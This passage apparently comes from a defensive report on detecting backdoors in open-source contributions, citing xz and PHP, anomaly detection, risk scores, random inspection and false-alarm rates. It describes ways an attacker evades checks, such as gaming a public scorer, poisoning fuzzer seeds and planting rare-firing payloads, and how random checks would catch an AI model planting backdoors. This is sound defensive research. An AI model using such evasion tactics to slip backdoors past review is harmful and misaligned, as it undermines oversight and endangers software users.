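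The size of a change is a weaker clue. *Towards Socio-Technical Topology-Aware Adaptive Threat Detection in Software Supply Chains* (2025) examined the history of xz and found that "Jia Tan", the account behind the backdoor, added an average of 89 lines per changed file, compared with 28 for the legitimate maintainer. But this compares only two people, and the Linux backdoor of 2003 needed just two lines.

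Where a change is made may be more useful, because an attacker has less freedom to choose it. A project can give a higher score to changes to password checks, build scripts or binary test files. The xz attackers used build scripts and binary test files. Such scoring wouldn't have helped the maintainers of OpenSSH, though, because the malicious code was in xz, a different project.

New code that the fuzzer can't run is also a warning sign, but a weak one in projects with poor harnesses. Kokkonis and colleagues point out that an attacker who makes code hard to reach also makes it stand out in coverage reports. They suggest this may be why the xz attackers disabled the project's automated fuzzing. A submission that turns off fuzzing or weakens a harness should get a high score for that alone.

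### Judging the contributor instead of the code

A commit under Rasmus Lerdorf's name added the PHP backdoor at about six in the morning, with the message "typo fix". Ganz, Ashraf and colleagues (2023), in *Detecting Backdoors in Collaboration Graphs of Software Repositories*, point out that Lerdorf's previous 20 commits to the main branch had all come after six in the evening. Their system looks for unusual commits like this one without analysing what the code does.

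Ganz and colleagues represent a project's history as a graph that links developers to their commits, and commits to the files and functions they changed. A neural network learns what normal histories look like and measures how far each new commit departs from them. They trained the network on 90 repositories with artificial anomalies added, such as a commit with another commit's message or a randomly chosen author.

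They tested the system on 19 repositories that contained real attacks, and it found 15 of them. On average, it also flagged about 11% of the harmless commits in each repository. Both figures need some care:

- Eleven of the 15 successes were small repositories infected by the same malware, and six of those had only one commit. In the eight larger projects, the system found four attacks.
- The 11% counts a project with seven commits as heavily as one with 2,295. Ganz and colleagues give 0.7% as the rate over all commits together, but the rates they list for the individual repositories imply about 2.3%.

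In PHP, the system flagged about 32 harmless commits out of 390 in a month. That is too many to block automatically, but Ganz and colleagues propose using the system only to select commits for closer attention. Running ROSA on the flagged commits would take about 2,200 core-hours, compared with 25,000 for all 390.

The misses are more worrying than the false alarms. Ganz and colleagues say two of the four happened because the maintainer planted the malicious code, so its author looked normal. Maintainers also planted the code in the other two, node-ipc and colors.js. A system that looks for unusual behaviour is good at noticing a stolen account, but a trusted insider has little reason to behave unusually.

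A patient outsider can become an insider, so *Beneath the Mask* (2025) looks at how quickly contributors gain privileged access. It finds this speed a promising signal of attacks like the one on xz, though an attacker who knows about the signal can respond by waiting longer.

Working hours and friendships with other developers mean little for AI agents, so a project has to judge an agent by its record. Meta requires each set of instructions for its code-writing agent to go 60 days without causing an incident before the resulting changes can skip human review. Such a record is reasonable evidence about accidents but much weaker evidence about backdoors. By the rule of three, 3,000 submissions with no backdoor found show only that fewer than about one in 1,000 contains one, and even that assumes somebody would have noticed every backdoor.

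### When the score is wrong

The plan for A, B and C is the best one only if the probabilities are right. Suppose that exactly one of the three has a backdoor. The chance of finding it depends on which one it is:

| Backdoor is in | Plan based on the score | Equal split |
|---|---|---|
| A | 96% | 74% |
| B | 57% | 74% |
| C | 0% | 74% |

Hong (2026), in *The true detection probability versus the subjective detection probability*, proves that a search plan can be the best one by the searcher's own estimates and still be worse in reality than another plan. The problem disappears with unlimited time, provided the searcher gave the true location some chance, but that doesn't help a project that has four hours and spends none of them on C.

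Two scores for the same submission can also disagree, for example if a model finds nothing wrong with a change but the contributor's history looks odd. A project could average the two scores and make one plan, or make a plan for each score and average the hours the plans assign to each check. Hong shows that averaging the plans can give better results in reality, even though it always looks worse when judged by the averaged scores.

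A scoring mistake might affect any submission, but an attacker will deliberately try to get a low score for malicious code. If the scorer is public, he can run it on his own code and revise the code until the score is low enough. He can also split a large change into small ones or build up a good record first. The more closely a project follows its scores, the more he gains, because a low enough score exempts his code from the expensive checks.

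Giving every submission a minimum amount of checking time removes that guarantee and barely reduces overall detection. If the project gives C 15 minutes and divides the rest as before, A gets 3.03 hours and B gets 0.72. The expected number of backdoors found falls by less than 1%, from 0.1014 to 0.1005. If C does have a backdoor, the chance of finding it rises from zero to 22%.

### Checking a random share

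ROSA took an hour and a half on average to find a backdoor, so running it for 15 minutes on every submission would miss most backdoors. It makes more sense to run such a slow check in full on a few submissions chosen at random. A fast tool such as Lily can still check every submission.

Suppose the project with 50 submissions a day can run ROSA on five of them. It could choose the three with the highest scores and pick two at random from the other 47. Each of those 47 would then have a 4.3% chance of a full run. If ROSA finds 87% of backdoors, as it did in the experiments, a backdoor in one of those 47 submissions would be caught 3.7% of the time.

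That risk is small for someone who needs to succeed only once, but it accumulates for an AI model that plants backdoors repeatedly. After 50 attempts, the chance of at least one detection is 1 − 0.963⁵⁰, or about 85%, and a single detection would give the project reason to re-examine everything else the model wrote.

The theory of inspection games covers how much checking it takes to deter an attacker. In these games, one player decides whether to break a rule and the other decides whether to inspect. *Inspection and crime prevention* (2013) explains why neither player can settle on a fixed choice. If the inspector always inspects, nobody breaks the rule and the inspections are wasted. If the inspector then stops, breaking the rule becomes worthwhile again. In the stable outcome, both players choose at random, with particular probabilities.

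Suppose a successful backdoor is worth 10 to the attacker. If he is caught, he loses an account with a good reputation, which is worth 40 to him. Honest code gains him nothing. The project gives a random share *q* of submissions a check that finds 90% of backdoors, so the attacker can expect:

10 × (1 − 0.9*q*) − 40 × 0.9*q* = 10 − 45*q*

The attacker's expected payoff from planting a backdoor is negative once *q* exceeds 22%. If the project checks a quarter of all submissions, he loses 1.25 on average by planting one and does better by submitting honest code.

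Random checks are more likely to deter an attacker who knows the rate. In *Recursive Inspection Games* (2014), an inspector publicly commits to a random inspection rate, using a method that others can verify. The other player obeys the rule if the rate is at or above the threshold. The project should announce the rate but keep each choice secret until the check is over. Otherwise, an attacker could withdraw any submission chosen for a check and resubmit it later.

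An attacker who uses a throwaway account has nothing to lose, and he can expect to gain 1 even if the project checks every submission. Random checks therefore work best combined with a full check of every submission from a new account. An attacker then has to do months of honest work before his submissions are checked less often, and he loses that work if he is caught. A government that can pay for many such accounts may accept the loss.

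Kokkonis and colleagues recommend random checks to counter one attack on Lily. An attacker first submits code that contains the trigger condition but no payload. The fuzzer may save inputs that satisfy the condition, and Lily will later treat those inputs as examples of normal behaviour. When the attacker adds the payload, the behaviour it causes also looks normal.

To simulate this, they added 100 triggering inputs to the saved seeds, and Lily's detection rate on commits fell from 90% to 54%. The hardened mode restores the detection rate by discarding every saved input on which the old and new versions make different types of system call. If the project received 50 submissions a day and used this mode on all of them, the mode would raise more than one false alarm a day. If the project used it on a random tenth of them, it would raise about one every eight days.

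Random checks also test the score. If a project examines only high-scoring submissions, it never learns what the low-scoring ones contain. A backdoor found by randomly checking a low-scoring submission shows that its score was too low.

### Why most alarms are false

Lily finds 90% of backdoors and raises a false alarm on 0.2% of harmless commits. If only one commit in 100,000 contains a backdoor, Lily would find an average of 0.9 backdoors per 100,000 commits and raise about 200 false alarms, so only about one alarm in 220 would be real.

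The result depends heavily on how common backdoors are, which nobody knows:

| Commits with a backdoor | Alarms that are real |
|---|---|
| 1 in 1,000 | about 1 in 3 |
| 1 in 10,000 | about 1 in 23 |
| 1 in 100,000 | about 1 in 220 |
| 1 in 1,000,000 | about 1 in 2,200 |

*MalTotal* (2026) reports a result at the favourable end of this range. Its scanner for malicious repositories searched about 120,000 repositories and flagged 1,553, of which reviewers rejected 502 as false alarms. The tool wrongly flagged only about 0.4% of harmless repositories, yet about a third of its alarms were false. That share stayed this low because nearly 1% of the repositories were malicious. If only one in 100,000 had been, the same rate of about 0.4% would have produced over 400 false alarms for each real one.

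Checking only high-scoring submissions makes the alarms more reliable but misses more backdoors. Suppose a score for malice worked as well as Meta's example for accidents, so that the top 10% of submissions contained 60% of the backdoors. If the project ran Lily only on that 10%, about one alarm in 38 would be real instead of one in 220, but Lily would find only 54% of the backdoors instead of 90%. Since Lily takes few resources to run, it makes more sense to run it on everything and use the score to decide which alarms to examine first.

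### What a replayable input saves

One real alarm in 220 is tolerable if alarms are quick to investigate, but not if each takes an afternoon. Lily's alarms come with an input that reproduces the suspicious behaviour and, on average, at most a dozen lines of code to read. If each takes two minutes, as ROSA's reports did, 200 false alarms take less than seven hours. A project with 50 submissions a day would take five and a half years to produce that many false alarms.

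An alarm based on a contributor's history comes with no such input. It marks a commit as unusual, and the reviewer then has to read the commit to work out whether it is harmful. Ganz and colleagues assume this takes two hours, so 200 false alarms would take 400 hours. But their system's false-alarm rate of 2.3% would produce about 2,300 false alarms for every 100,000 commits, or 4,600 hours of work. Such a system is therefore better used to choose which commits to run than to reject commits.

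An ordinary maintainer may need more than two minutes. The people who measured that time had built the tool, and most of Lily's false alarms on commits came from enormous merges, where it is harder to tell what the program should do. Someone who has dismissed 200 alarms in a row may also dismiss the next one without looking properly.

A script can do part of the checking before a person sees the alarm. One of Lily's false alarms came from a ProFTPD commit that made suspicious system calls in only one run out of 20. Replaying each reported input several times on both versions can reveal this kind of erratic behaviour. The project should move such alarms down the list but not delete them, because an attacker could write a payload that runs only one time in ten.
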